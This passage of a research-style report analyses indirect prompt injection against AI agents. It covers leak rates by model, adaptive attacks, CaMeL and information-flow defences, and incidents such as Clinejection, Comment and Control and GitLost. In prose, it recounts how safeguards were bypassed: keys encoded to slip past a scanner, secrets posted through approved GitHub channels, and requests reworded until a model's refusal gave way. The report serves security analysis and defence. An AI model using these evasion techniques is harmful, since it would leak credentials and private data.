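| Supabase: project scoping | Narrows private data | No, though the dashboard may fill it in | Theft within one project |
| Supabase: feature groups | None while `database` is on | Nearly all groups are on | The whole support-ticket attack |
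| GitHub: check for secrets | Narrows the outbound channel | Yes | Salaries, plans, project names and other ordinary text |
| GitHub: hidden-text filter | Narrows untrusted text | Yes | Instructions in visible plain English |
| GitHub: lockdown mode | Narrows untrusted text | No | Files, private repositories and possibly `list_issues` |
| GitHub: read-only mode | Removes the outbound channel | No | Data sent through other tools |
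| GitHub: hiding tools by token scope | None | Yes, for classic tokens | Every call the token permits |
| GitHub: labels on results | None without separate enforcement | Depends on the enforcing service | Everything, if nothing acts on the labels |
| Atlassian: write switch | Removes the outbound channel where writing is off | No; an administrator must block writing | Data sent through other tools |
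| Atlassian: rules on who may connect | None | Partly; listed AI companies can connect | Planted text read by an approved agent |
| Atlassian: hiding content from agents | Narrows private data or untrusted text | No; needs a paid plan | Content outside the policy; agents using API tokens |

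## Research in 2025 and 2026: how often agents obey planted text, and designs that limit the damage

Most protections that vendors turned on for everyone leave the final decision to the model, so their value depends on how often models obey planted text. The Invariant Labs and Cato demonstrations included no success rates, but academic researchers and AI developers have since measured them in controlled tests. The rates range from zero to more than 95%, depending mostly on the model and on how hard the attacker tries.

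### How many public tools could play a part

An attack of this kind needs tools that supply each part of the lethal trifecta. To find out how common such tools are, Zhao, Hou and colleagues (2025) collected 1,360 tool servers, with 12,230 tools, from public lists for *Parasites in the Toolchain*. A language model picked out 5,666 tools whose descriptions suggested a risk. The researchers then ran these tools in Cursor, using dummy secrets and planted text where they could, and three reviewers checked the logs.

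This confirmed 1,062 risky tools, or 8.7% of the total. 487 could bring in an outsider's text, 406 could read private data and 190 could send data out; a few could do more than one of these. The risky tools came from 370 servers, just over a quarter of the sample. Only two servers had tools of all three kinds, so an attacker would usually need a user who had installed a suitable combination of servers.

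The count of two is probably weak evidence about official tool servers. The researchers tested only servers that a user can start with a single command, and they couldn't register for about 30% of them, often because the service behind the server required a credit card or a company account. Servers published by large software companies usually require an account. The results for Gitee, a Chinese code host, also look low. The researchers classed 18 of its server's 20 tools as sources of outside text but none as a way to read private data or send it out, which is surprising for a service that hosts code.

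A second study, *No-Box Vulnerability Analysis* (Zhang, Hu and colleagues, 2026), looked at fewer and better-known servers. It examined 177 tools on 20 widely used servers and confirmed that 95 of the tools were open to indirect prompt injection. The study counted a tool as vulnerable if an outsider's instructions could reach the model through it, whether or not the model would obey them, because obedience varies so much with the wording and the model. The count therefore doesn't measure how often data theft would succeed.

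Their scanner flagged 143 of the tools, and 132 of those passed outside text to the model without cleaning it. Only six had an effective defence. Other tools were safe by accident, most often because they returned only a count or a status code, which left out the attacker's text. The scanner also found fields that a human reviewer could easily overlook, such as pull request titles and user profile biographies.

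Zhang and colleagues recommend doing deliberately what happened here by accident. If a manager only wants to know how many tickets are open, the server can return just the number, so the agent never sees what the customers wrote. This has almost no downside, but it doesn't help an agent whose job is to answer the tickets.

### Attack rates by model

Zhao and colleagues also ran complete attacks. They built ten chains of three tools, planted instructions in a web page or an email, asked Cursor to fetch it, and checked whether private data reached the attacker. Cursor ran without approval prompts. The researchers emphasise that nine of the ten chains leaked data at least once in ten runs, but only 36 of the 100 runs leaked data.

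One chain that ran a database query and then created an issue in Linear, a project tracker, leaked once in ten runs. In another, which used three tools from a single Microsoft 365 server, a planted email led the agent to list the user's old emails and send them out three times in ten. The only chain that never leaked ended with a tool for naming music collections. The researchers concluded that attacks work better when the tools are naturally related. If so, a helpdesk server is a convenient target, since reading a ticket, searching for related records and replying are all part of one job.

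The researchers then repeated one attack with different models. The agent had to fetch a web page, read a file on the user's computer and email it to the attacker. They tried three wordings (blunt, polite and encoded) in up to five client programs, with five runs of each. Adding up their results gives these totals:

| Model | Leaks | Rate |
|---|---|---|
| Claude Sonnet 4.5 | 0 of 75 | 0% |
| GPT-5 | 0 of 75 | 0% |
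| Claude 3.5 Haiku | 11 of 75 | 15% |
| GPT-4.1 | 12 of 75 | 16% |
| Gemini 2.5 Flash | 53 of 75 | 71% |
| DeepSeek R1 | 45 of 60 | 75% |

Leak rates vary widely between models. Switching from Gemini 2.5 Flash to GPT-5 would have protected a company more than any warning around query results. The client also matters for at least some models. GPT-4.1 leaked data in 9 of 15 runs in OpenAI's Codex, but in only 3 of 60 runs in other clients.

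The two zeros don't rule out leaks. With 75 runs, a true rate of up to about 4% could still produce none. The researchers also used the same three wordings for every model and didn't rewrite them for the models that refused, whereas Zenity's researcher rewrote her first Jira ticket when Cursor turned it down.

Models released in early 2026 still obeyed planted text fairly often in another test. Wizwand's *Indirect Prompt Injection on LivePI Total* (2026), a leaderboard page, lists attack success rates from 10.7% for Claude Opus 4.6 to 29.6% for Gemini 3.1 Pro. Rates from different benchmarks can't be compared directly, because one set of attacks may be harder to resist than another.

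### Attackers who adapt

Most tests use a fixed list of attacks, and a defence can do well by blocking those attacks. To measure how much difference this makes, researchers from OpenAI, Anthropic, Google DeepMind and several other organisations designed attacks against each of 12 published defences (Nasr, Carlini and colleagues, *The Attacker Moves Second*, October 2025). Most of these defences had originally been reported to keep attackers' success rates near zero.

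In their automated attacks, a program proposes wordings, scores them, writes new versions of the best and repeats the process. The researchers also held a competition in which more than 500 people tried to break the defences by hand. The attacks succeeded more than 90% of the time against most of the 12 defences.

Two of the defences closely resemble what a tool server's maker might add. Spotlighting uses markers to separate trusted text from the rest, and prompt sandwiching repeats the user's request after the outside text as a reminder. Supabase's warnings around query results are similar. On AgentDojo, a benchmark that plants instructions in the data agents read during simulated tasks, the standard attacks succeeded as little as 1% of the time against these defences. The adaptive attack succeeded more than 95% of the time against both.

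One planted text that succeeded against prompt sandwiching posed as an access check the agent had to complete before continuing the user's task. Reminding the model of that task doesn't help here, because the model treats the check as part of it. The attack on Cline in *GitInject* worked in much the same way, by presenting its request as a routine diagnostic.

Nasr and colleagues gave their attackers plenty of computing power and a score after every attempt. Someone who submits a support ticket usually gets no score or explanation. But because the official tool servers and the models are available to everyone, an attacker can set up an account, connect the same server to the same model and test wordings until one works. They still won't know the target's standing instructions or what other tools its agent has. A determined attacker's success rate probably lies between the two figures, and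 there is no good reason to assume it is close to 1%.

### Injection results in the 2026 system cards

AI developers publish their own measurements in system cards, which describe how they tested a new model. Anthropic's cards have shown a large improvement within a year. The Decoder's *Claude Opus 4.5 resists prompt injections better than rivals* reports that a single strong attack worked 4.7% of the time against Opus 4.5, which was released in late 2025.

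In the February 2026 system card for Claude Opus 4.6, the success rate of prompt injection varied widely by setting. According to VentureBeat, the attack failed in all 200 attempts in a restricted coding environment. When the model operated a computer through its graphical interface without safeguards, a single attempt succeeded 17.8% of the time, and the success rate within 200 attempts was 78.6%. With safeguards, the rate within 200 attempts was 57.1%.

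Claude Opus 5 followed in July. Claude models had nearly reached the limit of the old benchmark, so Anthropic tested Opus 5 on a new one it had developed with the security company Gray Swan, the UK AI Security Institute and its US counterpart. TechFeed describes 28 scenarios covering coding, tool use and graphical interfaces, with 1,130 attacks. Attackers succeeded 0.2% of the time with one attempt and 2.0% within 15 attempts, compared with 0.5% and 5.5% for Opus 4.8. The Decoder's *Opus 5 may have solved browser-based prompt injection* reports that in a separate test of browser agents, no attack succeeded in any of 129 scenarios.

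In September, Anthropic's *System Card* (2026) for Claude Mythos 5.1 called it the company's most robust model so far on the same kind of benchmark. Three weeks later, the *System Card* (2026) for Claude Opus 5.5 reported results similar to or better than those of Opus 5 on every injection test, with one exception. Digital Matters' *Claude Opus 5.5 Prompt Injection* (2026) explains that the model got worse at resisting instructions in text that users paste in themselves. A support worker does this when copying a customer's email into a chat window, so it may now be safer to give the agent access to tickets through a tool server.

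Cheaper models, which companies are more likely to use for a long queue of routine tickets, have also become better at ignoring planted text. *Anthropic's new budget model gets much better at ignoring hidden commands* (Pogorelec, 2026) describes Claude Haiku 5.5, released in October, as designed for quick, repetitive work.

These are a developer's figures about its own products, though the involvement of two government institutes makes the main benchmark more credible. Nasr and colleagues raise a bigger worry, that testing against a collection of existing attacks can make a model look safer than it would be against someone who studied it. In a small example of this, researchers at the security company Reco gave Claude Fable 5 a sales record with a note telling the agent to look up an unrelated company's deals. The agent had standing instructions never to follow instructions found in records,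 but it ran the query anyway and explained that it was making sure the user didn't interfere with an existing deal. Reco sells security for business software, and a single case can't show how often this happens, but the test resembles the Salesforce attacks much more closely than a browser test does.

### What a 0.2% success rate means for a helpdesk

A support desk may handle thousands of tickets a month, and an attacker can submit as many as they like. If an agent reads every ticket, each planted ticket has the same chance *p* of success, and the attempts are independent, then the chance that at least one of *n* planted tickets succeeds is 1 − (1 − *p*)ⁿ.

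At the 0.2% success rate per ticket measured for Opus 5, an attacker who plants 100 tickets has an 18% chance of at least one success. The chance rises to 50% with about 350 tickets and 86% with 1,000.

The independence assumption is doing a lot of work in this calculation, and the published results for repeated attempts make it possible to check it:

| Model | One attempt | Number of attempts | Predicted if independent | Measured |
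|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Opus 4.5 | 4.7% | 10 | 38% | 33.6% |
| Claude Opus 4.5 | 4.7% | 100 | 99% | 63% |
| Claude Opus 4.8 | 0.5% | 15 | 7.2% | 5.5% |
| Claude Opus 5 | 0.2% | 15 | 3.0% | 2.0% |

The formula overestimates success every time, and by a wide margin at 100 attempts, probably because the average rate combines situations with very different rates. If an attack always worked in 5% of scenarios and never in the others, its success rate would be 5% after one attempt and still 5% after 100. The 86% above is therefore best treated as an upper estimate for an attacker who keeps sending tickets of the same quality to one company. An attacker who learned from each failure could do better than the formula predicts, as the adaptive attacks show.

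Hundreds of strange tickets might also alert the support staff. Sending one ticket to each of many companies would be less conspicuous, and Zenity easily found hundreds of suitable mailboxes through Google. If 1,000 companies used agents with a 0.2% attack success rate, the attacker could expect two successes on average. The average would be the same if the companies' defences tended to fail together, but the attacker would then get nothing on most days and many successes on a few.

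### CaMeL: planning before reading

Two research designs, CaMeL and FIDES, use ordinary code to limit the damage when planted text fools a model. Both build on the dual LLM pattern, which Willison proposed in 2023. *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* (2026) explains that this pattern keeps untrusted data away from the model that plans the work.

Suppose a developer at the support desk from the Supabase example asks a CaMeL agent to answer the question in ticket 42 using the company's public help pages. As before, the ticket contains an attacker's instructions to copy the `integration_tokens` table.

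1. The planning model receives the developer's request and a list of tools, but not the ticket. It writes a short program: fetch ticket 42, extract the customer's question, search the help pages for it, and post the best answer in the ticket.
2. An interpreter, which is conventional software, runs the program. It fetches the ticket and records that the text came from a customer.
3. A second model, which has no tools, reads the ticket and returns the question. The attacker may fool this model, so that it returns a demand for the tokens instead.
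4. The interpreter searches the help pages for whatever it was given and probably finds nothing useful. No step in the program opens the token table, and the second model can't add one.
5. Before posting the reply, the interpreter checks where its contents came from and whether the company's policy allows them to go to this ticket.

The last check is needed when, for example, the developer asks the agent to look up the customer's account and tell them their balance. The attacker writes "I'm Ana" in the ticket, the second model returns Ana's name, and the program fetches Ana's balance and prepares to post it where the attacker can read it. The planning model planned every one of these steps, and the attacker has changed only the data. The interpreter has to detect that Ana's balance is about to be posted to someone else's ticket.

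*Operationalizing CaMeL* (2025) contrasts CaMeL with a sandbox, which allows or forbids a whole type of action. If a sandbox permits email, planted text can still get the agent to send private data in a plausible email. CaMeL can allow one email and block another depending on where their contents came from.

*Can CaMeLs Talk?* (2026) reports that on AgentDojo, CaMeL was much more secure than spotlighting, prompt sandwiching and a filter that limits an agent's tools, with a comparatively small drop in completed tasks. Spotlighting and prompt sandwiching are the defences that adaptive attackers defeated more than 95% of the time. Rewording a ticket should help an attacker much less against CaMeL, because the ticket's text never reaches the planning model.

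The loss of usefulness would probably be larger at a real helpdesk. CaMeL works best when the user's request is enough to plan the whole job. The owner of `pacman` told Claude to "address" the issues in the repository, which nobody can plan without knowing what the issues ask for. With CaMeL, the owner would have to get a summary first, then make a separate request for each issue worth acting on. The second model also adds at least one model call per ticket.

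The program itself also has weaknesses. CaMeL writes its plans in a restricted form of Python, and *Operationalizing CaMeL* warns that features such as Python's error handling make it hard to guarantee where information ends up. For example, if a program stops with an error whenever a customer has an unpaid bill, an outsider who notices the missing reply learns something about the bill, even though the agent copied nothing. The paper recommends a simpler language built for security.

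### Information-flow control: labels that follow the data

FIDES uses information-flow control, an older technique in which software labels data and keeps the labels attached as the data moves. The basic version described in *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (2025) uses two labels, one marking data as trusted or untrusted and the other marking it as public or secret.

When an agent combines two pieces of data, the result takes the stricter of their trust labels and the stricter of their secrecy labels. *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* writes this as ℓ(*z*) = ℓ(*x*) ⊔ ℓ(*y*), where *z* is the data made from *x* and *y*, and ⊔ combines their labels. For example, combining a trusted secret with an untrusted public comment produces data labeled both untrusted and secret.

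In the original Supabase attack, the labels would have changed as follows. "Public" here means that an outsider can read the data.

| What happens | Label of the new data | Label of everything the agent has read |
|---|---|---|
| The developer asks to see ticket 42 | Trusted, public | Trusted, public |
| The agent reads the ticket | Untrusted, public | Untrusted, public |
| The agent reads `integration_tokens` | Trusted, secret | Untrusted, secret |
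| The agent tries to write in ticket 42 | None | The write fails, because the attacker can read the ticket |

The labels record where the text in the new row came from, which Postgres did not. The rule in the last row doesn't require anyone to judge whether the ticket looks suspicious.

A company could also adopt a stricter policy that stops the agent from opening secret tables once it has read untrusted text, so the tokens would never enter its context. But a support agent that couldn't look up an order after reading the customer's complaint would be close to useless. The more permissive policy is enough as long as it covers every way data could leave, including web requests, links and the ticket itself.

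Two levels of secrecy are too few for a helpdesk, where Ana may read her own tickets but the attacker may not read them. The label can instead list the people allowed to read the data. When an agent combines Ana's ticket with the attacker's, only people on both lists may read the result, so only the company's staff can see it. This is close to vidarh's rule of shared permissions, except that the agent can still read both tickets and is limited only in where it can send the result.

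Labels tend to spread. After the agent reads one untrusted ticket, its whole context is labeled untrusted, and a strict policy would then block much of what it does next. FIDES reduces this problem by storing the output of outside tools in variables. *Extending the Formalism and Theoretical Foundations of Cryptography to AI* (2026) notes that the agent can't base an action on the contents of a variable without further secure processing. An agent could therefore move a ticket between queues without being influenced by its text.

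Like Ntousakis's SAMOS, information-flow control blocks the harmless use of a private settings file to update a public example, because the label covers the whole file. A person would have to approve the exception, but an occasional prompt about private data leaving the company is easier to take seriously than a prompt for every call.

The company behind the service is in the best position to supply the labels. The labels in GitHub's tool server record the same two properties as the basic version of FIDES, but a separate service still has to enforce them.

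Helpdesk data would be harder to label than GitHub data. GitHub records which account opened an issue and whether a repository is private. A database like the one in the Supabase demonstration identifies the table a row is in, but not whether the text in it came from a customer or an employee, unless the app's developer recorded that. A sync between Zendesk and Jira can lose the same information.

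## February to July 2026: agents that run unattended in GitHub workflows

In Invariant Labs' demonstration, Claude read the planted issue because the owner of `pacman` asked it to. By 2026, thousands of projects had connected agents to GitHub Actions, GitHub's automation service, where an agent can start automatically when a stranger opens an issue. Nobody is present to approve the agent's tool calls or notice an odd answer.

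### From a request to a trigger

Software projects have long used GitHub Actions to test and publish their code. A workflow is a file in the repository that lists the steps to run and the event that starts them, such as a new issue. GitHub runs the steps on a runner, usually a temporary virtual machine. According to Microsoft, the runner may receive the project's code, a GitHub access token, and secrets such as cloud credentials and keys for publishing packages.

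A traditional workflow runs commands that the maintainers wrote in advance. An agentic workflow includes an agent that reads a new issue and decides what to do. Maintainers use such agents to label bug reports, review pull requests and answer questions. *GitInject* points out that these agents meet all three conditions of the lethal trifecta, because they read text from anonymous users, hold a token for the repository and can post public comments.

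These workflows are easier to attack than a helpdesk. The attacker decides when the agent runs and can run it again by opening another issue. If the repository is public, the attacker can also read the workflow file, which shows the agent's tools and usually its instructions, then copy the workflow into their own repository and try different wordings until one works. This puts them in nearly the same position as the adaptive attackers in Nasr and colleagues' tests.

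Daelman's *PromptPwnd*, written for the security company Aikido, described the weakness and reported that it affected at least five Fortune 500 companies. Google's repository for its coding agent, Gemini CLI, had the same weakness, which Google patched within four days.

### Clinejection: a theft that reached developers' computers

In February 2026, someone used this weakness in a real attack on Cline, the coding agent that later leaked a list of private repositories in the *GitInject* tests. Cline's maintainers had set up Claude to sort new issues. SafeDep's *AI Agent Cline v2.3.0 Compromised* reports that any GitHub user could start Claude by opening an issue, and that Claude could edit files and run shell commands. The workflow also copied the issue's title into Claude's prompt, so an attacker could use the title to tell Claude which commands to run, as Willison (2026) explained.

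The security researcher Adnan Khan found the flaw and published it on 9 February. Snyk's *How “Clinejection” Turned an AI Bot into a Supply Chain Attack* (2026) describes how the attack went from steering the agent that sorted issues to altering the cache, the files that GitHub Actions stores to speed up later runs. An attacker who controls one workflow can leave altered files in the cache for another workflow to load. In this case the other workflow published Cline's releases and had the keys to do so.

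On 17 February, an unknown attacker published an unauthorised version of Cline on npm, the main registry for JavaScript packages. For about eight hours, anyone who updated Cline's command-line program also got OpenClaw, a different AI agent. grith described the attack in *A GitHub Issue Title Compromised 4,000 Developer Machines*.

The theft probably happened earlier. An independent investigation, *Agent Compromised by Agent To Deploy an Agent*, found that the attacker had spotted Khan's test in a public repository and used it before he published his report. According to grith, Cline's team tried to replace the exposed keys but deleted the wrong one and didn't notice the mistake until 11 February. The stolen npm key still worked six days later.

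Cline called the incident an "unauthorized publication" and rated its severity as low, which seems too mild. OpenClaw is a real product, not malware, but whoever held the publishing credentials could have sent those developers anything. The attacker stole credentials, unlike the `pacman` demonstration, which took private files. The incident shows that someone outside a research team was willing to put instructions in an issue.

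### Comment and Control: secrets returned through GitHub

On 15 April, the security engineer Aonan Guan published attacks on three vendors' agents, two of which he had tested with researchers from Johns Hopkins University. The title of his *Comment And Control Prompt Injection Credential Theft* (2026) plays on "command and control", the server from which an attacker normally directs hacked machines. Guan didn't need such a server because he wrote his instructions on GitHub and the agents put the stolen secrets there too.

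| Agent | Where the attacker writes | Where the secrets appear | Bounty |
|---|---|---|---|
| Anthropic's Claude Code Security Review | Title of a pull request | A comment on the pull request, presented as a security finding | $100 |
| Google's Gemini CLI Action | Title of an issue and comments on it | A public comment on the issue | $1,337 |
| GitHub's Copilot Agent | Hidden text in an issue | A file in a new pull request | $500 |

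The first two agents started without any action by the victim. Claude's output also went into the workflow's log, which maintainers rarely read. An attacker could collect the keys there without leaving a trace in the pull request.

GitHub's default settings limit the Claude attack. Outsiders usually submit pull requests from a fork, their own copy of the repository, and GitHub doesn't give secrets to workflows triggered by these pull requests unless the maintainers change the setting. Guan says some repositories do change it, but doesn't say how many.

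Copilot was the hardest target. A maintainer had to assign the issue to it, though the maintainer would see only a harmless request, because the instructions were in an HTML comment that GitHub doesn't display. GitHub had also added three protections around the agent, and Guan got past each of them:

- A filter removed secrets from the settings of any shell command the agent ran. It didn't remove them from the other programs on the same machine, and the agent could read those.
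- A scanner checked the agent's changes for keys before they left the machine. The agent encoded the keys first, so the scanner didn't recognise them.
- A firewall blocked connections to unapproved sites. GitHub was an approved site, and the agent put the keys in a pull request there.

Guan recovered four credentials from the process that ran the agent's MCP server. The server kept its access token on the same machine as the agent, which was reading text written by a stranger.

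The vendors' replies varied. Anthropic rated the severity of its flaw 9.4 out of 10 and paid $100. It blocked the command Guan had used to list running programs, and said the action "is not designed to be hardened against prompt injection". Guan pointed out that another common command gives the same information, and he rightly recommends a short list of permitted tools instead of a growing list of forbidden ones. Anthropic's disclaimer is hard to act on, because a project most needs a security review when the code comes from a stranger.

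GitHub first closed Guan's report as a known issue that it couldn't reproduce. He sent evidence from Copilot's code that the filter existed to prevent this kind of leak, and GitHub reopened the report. It then called the exposure a previously identified "architectural limitation" and said it was looking for ways to restrict it further.

### Microsoft's tests and the attempts it saw

In June, Microsoft described a similar gap in another Anthropic product, the Claude Code action. As a precaution, the action ran the agent's shell commands in a sandbox without the project's secrets when the workflow's settings let outsiders start the agent. But the tool for reading files ran outside the sandbox and could open a system file that contained Anthropic's API key. Microsoft planted text that described the task as a compliance review and asked for the key in a slightly altered form. This got the key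 past both Claude's safeguards against revealing keys and GitHub's scanner. Microsoft had reported the flaw to Anthropic on 29 April, and Anthropic blocked access to such files on 5 May.

Microsoft had started this research after seeing injection attempts in public repositories that used several vendors' agents. In one attempt, the attacker posed as someone requesting a diagnostic feature and gave an agent step-by-step instructions to find a documentation page, add an invisible image tag to it and open a pull request with the change. If a maintainer had merged it, a script would have run in visitors' browsers and stolen their login sessions.

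The agent opened the pull request, so the injection worked. The repository was a fork of a well-known documentation project, and Microsoft believes the attacker was using it to practise. The incident is good evidence that people outside research teams are developing such attacks, but it doesn't show that anyone lost data.

Microsoft advised maintainers to follow the "Agents Rule of Two", which allows a workflow at most two of three abilities: reading untrusted input, reaching sensitive systems or secrets, and changing things or communicating externally. The rule is slightly stricter than avoiding the lethal trifecta, because it counts any change, not only those that could carry data out. For safeguards against the theft of secrets, Microsoft referred readers to the design of GitHub Agentic Workflows, which Noma attacked a month later.

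### How many workflows a stranger could steer

Wang, Hou and colleagues (2026), in *Demystifying and Detecting Agentic Workflow Injection Vulnerabilities in GitHub Actions*, measured how common the weakness is. They studied 1,033 AI-related actions (reusable steps that maintainers add to workflows) and collected 13,392 workflows that use such actions, from 10,792 repositories.

The program TaintAWI marks any text that an outsider can write and follows it through the workflow. It lists workflows in which that text reaches either the prompt of an agent that has tools or a model whose answer a later script acts on. It leaves out a workflow if an effective check prevents outsiders from starting the model. An instruction to ignore prompt injection doesn't count as a check.

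| Step | Workflows |
|---|---|
| Examined | 13,392 |
| An outsider's text reaches a model that can affect something | 881 |
| No effective check on who can start it | 519 |
| Confirmed as exploitable by manual review | 496 |
| Not previously reported by anyone | 343 |

The confirmed cases are 3.7% of the sample, and 429 of them began with the title or body of an issue. The true number of cases may be somewhat higher. The researchers checked 400 workflows that only other scanners had flagged and found 13 cases that TaintAWI had missed.

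The results differ widely between actions. Anthropic's Claude Code action appeared in 5,212 workflows but only 13 confirmed cases. GitHub's `ai-inference`, a simple action that sends a prompt to a model and returns the answer, appeared in 795 workflows and 393 confirmed cases. The most likely explanation is that Anthropic's action restricts who can start it, while GitHub's does not. Only 21 of the 1,033 actions had such a restriction. Maintainers seldom add their own, as only 56 of the 881 workflows had an effective check outside the action.

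These figures measure how often a stranger can influence a workflow, which is much broader than data theft. Most of the confirmed cases follow the second pattern, in which the model only returns text. If the script uses that text to label an issue, an attacker may achieve nothing worse than a wrong label. In 391 cases the workflow could change something on GitHub, such as by posting a comment, but the paper doesn't count how many of these could also read private data. The reviewers judged the workflows by reading them, and some would be hard to attack in practice because a secret is missing or the workflow no longer runs.

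Companies that make the agents had the same problem. OpenAI's repository for its Codex agent let anyone start a workflow that labels issues, and an example workflow that Google published for others to copy was also vulnerable. Wang and colleagues prioritized 187 of the new cases but could report only 85, because the other 102 repositories had no private reporting channel. They got 26 replies, and maintainers accepted or fixed 24 of the cases, two of which already have a CVE.

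They recommend checking the model's answer against a fixed list, so that a script accepts "bug" or "question" and rejects everything else. This works whatever the issue says. Their suggestion to give the agent only the issue's number and let it fetch the text with a restricted command is less useful. It keeps a stranger's words out of the maintainer's instructions, but the agent still reads them a moment later. Claude fetched the Pac-Man issue through a tool in this way.

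### GitHub Agentic Workflows and safe outputs

GitHub Agentic Workflows is GitHub's system for running agents in Actions. It first became available in February 2026, according to SC Media's *'GitLost' prompt injection leaks private repos via GitHub Agentic Workflows*. A maintainer writes a file that lists the permissions and then describes the job in ordinary language, and a compiler turns the file into a workflow. The agent can be Copilot, Claude or one of several others.

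GitHub's *Under the hood* explains the design. GitHub assumes that an agent will try to read and write things it shouldn't, and that it will "abuse legitimate channels to perform unwanted actions". The safeguards therefore don't depend on the agent behaving well. With the default settings, a workflow that answers new issues runs like this:

1. GitHub starts the agent in an isolated container. A firewall lets it connect only to approved sites.
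2. The agent's keys stay outside the container. One separate program holds the key for the language model, and another holds the token for GitHub's tool server. Both pass on the agent's requests without showing it the keys.
3. The agent reads the issue through the tool server, which has read-only access.
4. To reply, the agent submits the text of a comment. Nothing appears on GitHub yet, because the system only records the request.
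5. After the agent has stopped, software checks the request. It must be a type of write that the maintainer declared in advance, and it must be within the limit, which is one comment by default. The software also removes secrets and links to unapproved sites.
6. A separate job, which does have permission to write, posts the comment.

GitHub calls steps 4 to 6 safe outputs. GitHub's *Safe Outputs* lists dozens of types a maintainer can allow, from adding a label to merging a pull request. An optional scan by another AI model can block the write if it detects prompt injection, leaked secrets or malicious code.

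This design is an improvement on the workflows that Guan and Microsoft attacked. Those attacks depended on finding keys on the machine where the agent ran, and in this design the agent's container has none unless the maintainer puts them there. If the maintainer has allowed the agent only one comment, it also can't open 50 pull requests, even if it obeys a stranger's instructions.

But step 5 checks the type, number and format of the writes, not whether the person reading the comment is allowed to see the information in it. This matters little if the agent can read only the public repository it works in. However, a maintainer can let it read other repositories by adding a personal access token that covers them, as GitHub explains in its FAQ.

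### GitLost: a private README in a permitted comment

Noma Security, which had found ForcedLeak in Salesforce the year before, attacked a workflow of this kind and published the result in early July 2026 under the name GitLost. InfoQ's *Indirect Prompt Injection Exploits GitHub's AI Agent to Leak Private Repository Data* (2026) describes the configuration. The workflow started whenever an issue was assigned. The agent read the issue's title and body and could reply through the `add-comment` safe output. It could also read the organisation's other repositories, including private ones.

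The researchers opened an issue in a public repository. It looked like a message from a vice president of sales following up on a customer meeting, and it included a question about the contents of README files. After the issue was assigned, the agent, which ran on Copilot, fetched one README from a public repository and another from a private repository called `testlocal`. It then posted the contents of both in a public comment.

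Copilot's guardrails refused the request when the researchers made it on its own, so the researchers reworded it until one version got through. Expert Insights' *Researchers Trick Misconfigured GitHub AI Agent Into Leaking a Private Repo* (2026) reports that the successful wording made the request look like part of the agent's existing task. The same idea had worked against prompt sandwiching and on Cline and Cursor, so the problem isn't specific to one model.

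The attack works only if the issue is assigned, a step Noma left out when it said that an attacker only had to open an issue "and wait". An outsider can't normally assign issues in someone else's repository, so a maintainer or an automatic rule has to do it. In the demonstration, an automatic rule assigned the issue. Many projects assign new issues automatically, but where a person does it, that person could notice that it is odd for a sales executive to ask for a README on a public page.

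The repositories belonged to Noma, and the stolen file was a test README. Noma published the issue and the record of the workflow run, so readers can check that the leak happened. Like Invariant's demonstration, this one is little evidence of how often the attack would succeed.

### Why the safeguards let the comment through

If Noma's workflow kept GitHub's default protections, nearly all of them did their job:

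| Safeguard | Effect during the attack | Why the README still got out |
|---|---|---|
| Firewall | Blocked unapproved sites | The agent sent the data to GitHub |
| Keys kept outside the container | The agent never saw the access token | The tool server used the token to fetch the file for it |
| Read-only access | The agent could not change a repository directly | It needed only to read the private file |
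| Safe outputs | Allowed only the kind of write the maintainer had declared | The maintainer had declared comments |
| Removal of secrets | Looked for keys and passwords | A README is ordinary text |
| Copilot's refusal | Stopped the first wording | A reworded request got through |

Only the last one failed, and it was the only one that addressed whether the agent should reveal this file to this reader. The rest would have handled the comment the same way if it had contained a helpful answer.

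Information-flow control would have blocked the comment. The text from `testlocal` would have kept its private label, so the job in step 6 would not have posted it publicly. In *Under the hood*, GitHub said it planned controls that account for whether a repository is public or private.

The optional AI scan might have caught the comment too, but it would have had to recognise the sales executive's message as an attack, which Copilot had failed to do. Press accounts of GitLost don't mention whether the scan was on.

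By September 2026, GitHub also had a safeguard that automatically hid content written by outsiders from agentic workflows in public repositories. An agent with this filter would not have seen an issue from a stranger. But as with lockdown mode, GitHub tells maintainers to turn the filter off for workflows that sort new issues, and workflows that answer the public need the same exception.

### "Critical vulnerability" or "misconfigured workflow"

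News reports disagreed about what Noma had found. SecurityWeek's *Critical Vulnerability Exposes GitHub Agentic Workflows to Prompt Injection* and SiliconANGLE's *‘GitLost’ vulnerability let GitHub’s AI workflows leak private repositories* (2026) treated it as a critical flaw in GitHub's product. Expert Insights said the agent was misconfigured and blamed an "over-permissioned workflow" and a guardrail that an attacker could bypass through wording.

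The second description fits the facts of the demonstration better. An agentic workflow can't read an organisation's other private repositories until someone gives it a token for them. Whoever set up Noma's workflow had done that and had also let the agent reply publicly to strangers, a combination that Microsoft's Rule of Two forbids. If the token had covered only the public repository, the same issue would have produced a comment with nothing private in it. Noma also didn't show how many organisations have a similar workflow, and one would need to know that to call the problem critical.

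Still, "misconfigured" puts too much of the blame on the maintainer, because each setting has an ordinary use. An agent that answers bug reports gives better answers if it can read the shared library in another repository, and GitHub documents how to give it that access. A maintainer who had read about isolated containers and safe outputs could easily believe that the design protected against prompt injection. Sasi Levi, who led the research at Noma, told SC Media that the danger comes from a mismatch between where an agent has permissions and where its inputs come from. That mismatch is hard to see when each setting looks reasonable.

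GitHub never gave the attacker access to `testlocal`, and the agent could not have opened it either without the extra token. The repository's privacy protected it until the organisation gave that token to an agent that takes requests from the public. The more sweeping conclusion of the technology executive Vijendra Malhotra, quoted by InfoQ, that "the private repo was never a security boundary" therefore goes too far.

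As far as the first reports show, GitHub did not change the product's code in response. Noma had suggested a documentation note warning teams about sharing keys between repositories. In July, The Next Web's *'GitLost'* reported that GitHub had not added the note or answered questions from the news site The Register.

A note would help, but the compiler could also warn maintainers when a stranger's issue can start a workflow that has a token for other repositories and can comment publicly. Before the agent runs, the compiler reads the settings at the top of the workflow file, which list the triggering event, any additional token and the permitted writes. The compiler could also require a person to approve comments from such workflows. GitHub already offers this approval step as an option and enforces it itself, so the agent can't skip it. Reading each reply would take away some of the benefit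 of an unattended agent. But workflows that don't touch private repositories could still run without a reviewer, and someone who reviews only the risky replies is more likely to notice text from a private README in one.

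## June 2026: false error reports in Sentry steer coding agents

A coding agent on a developer's computer can usually run commands with the developer's permissions. Tenet Security's *A Fake Bug Report Hijacks Your AI Coding Agent* (2026) describes an attack in which a false error report in Sentry, an error-tracking service, leads such an agent to run an attacker's program. Tenet, a start-up that sells protection for AI agents, calls this agentjacking. Invariant Labs and General Analysis had attacked only their own test accounts, but Tenet also tried its method on other organisations.

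### A key that every visitor receives

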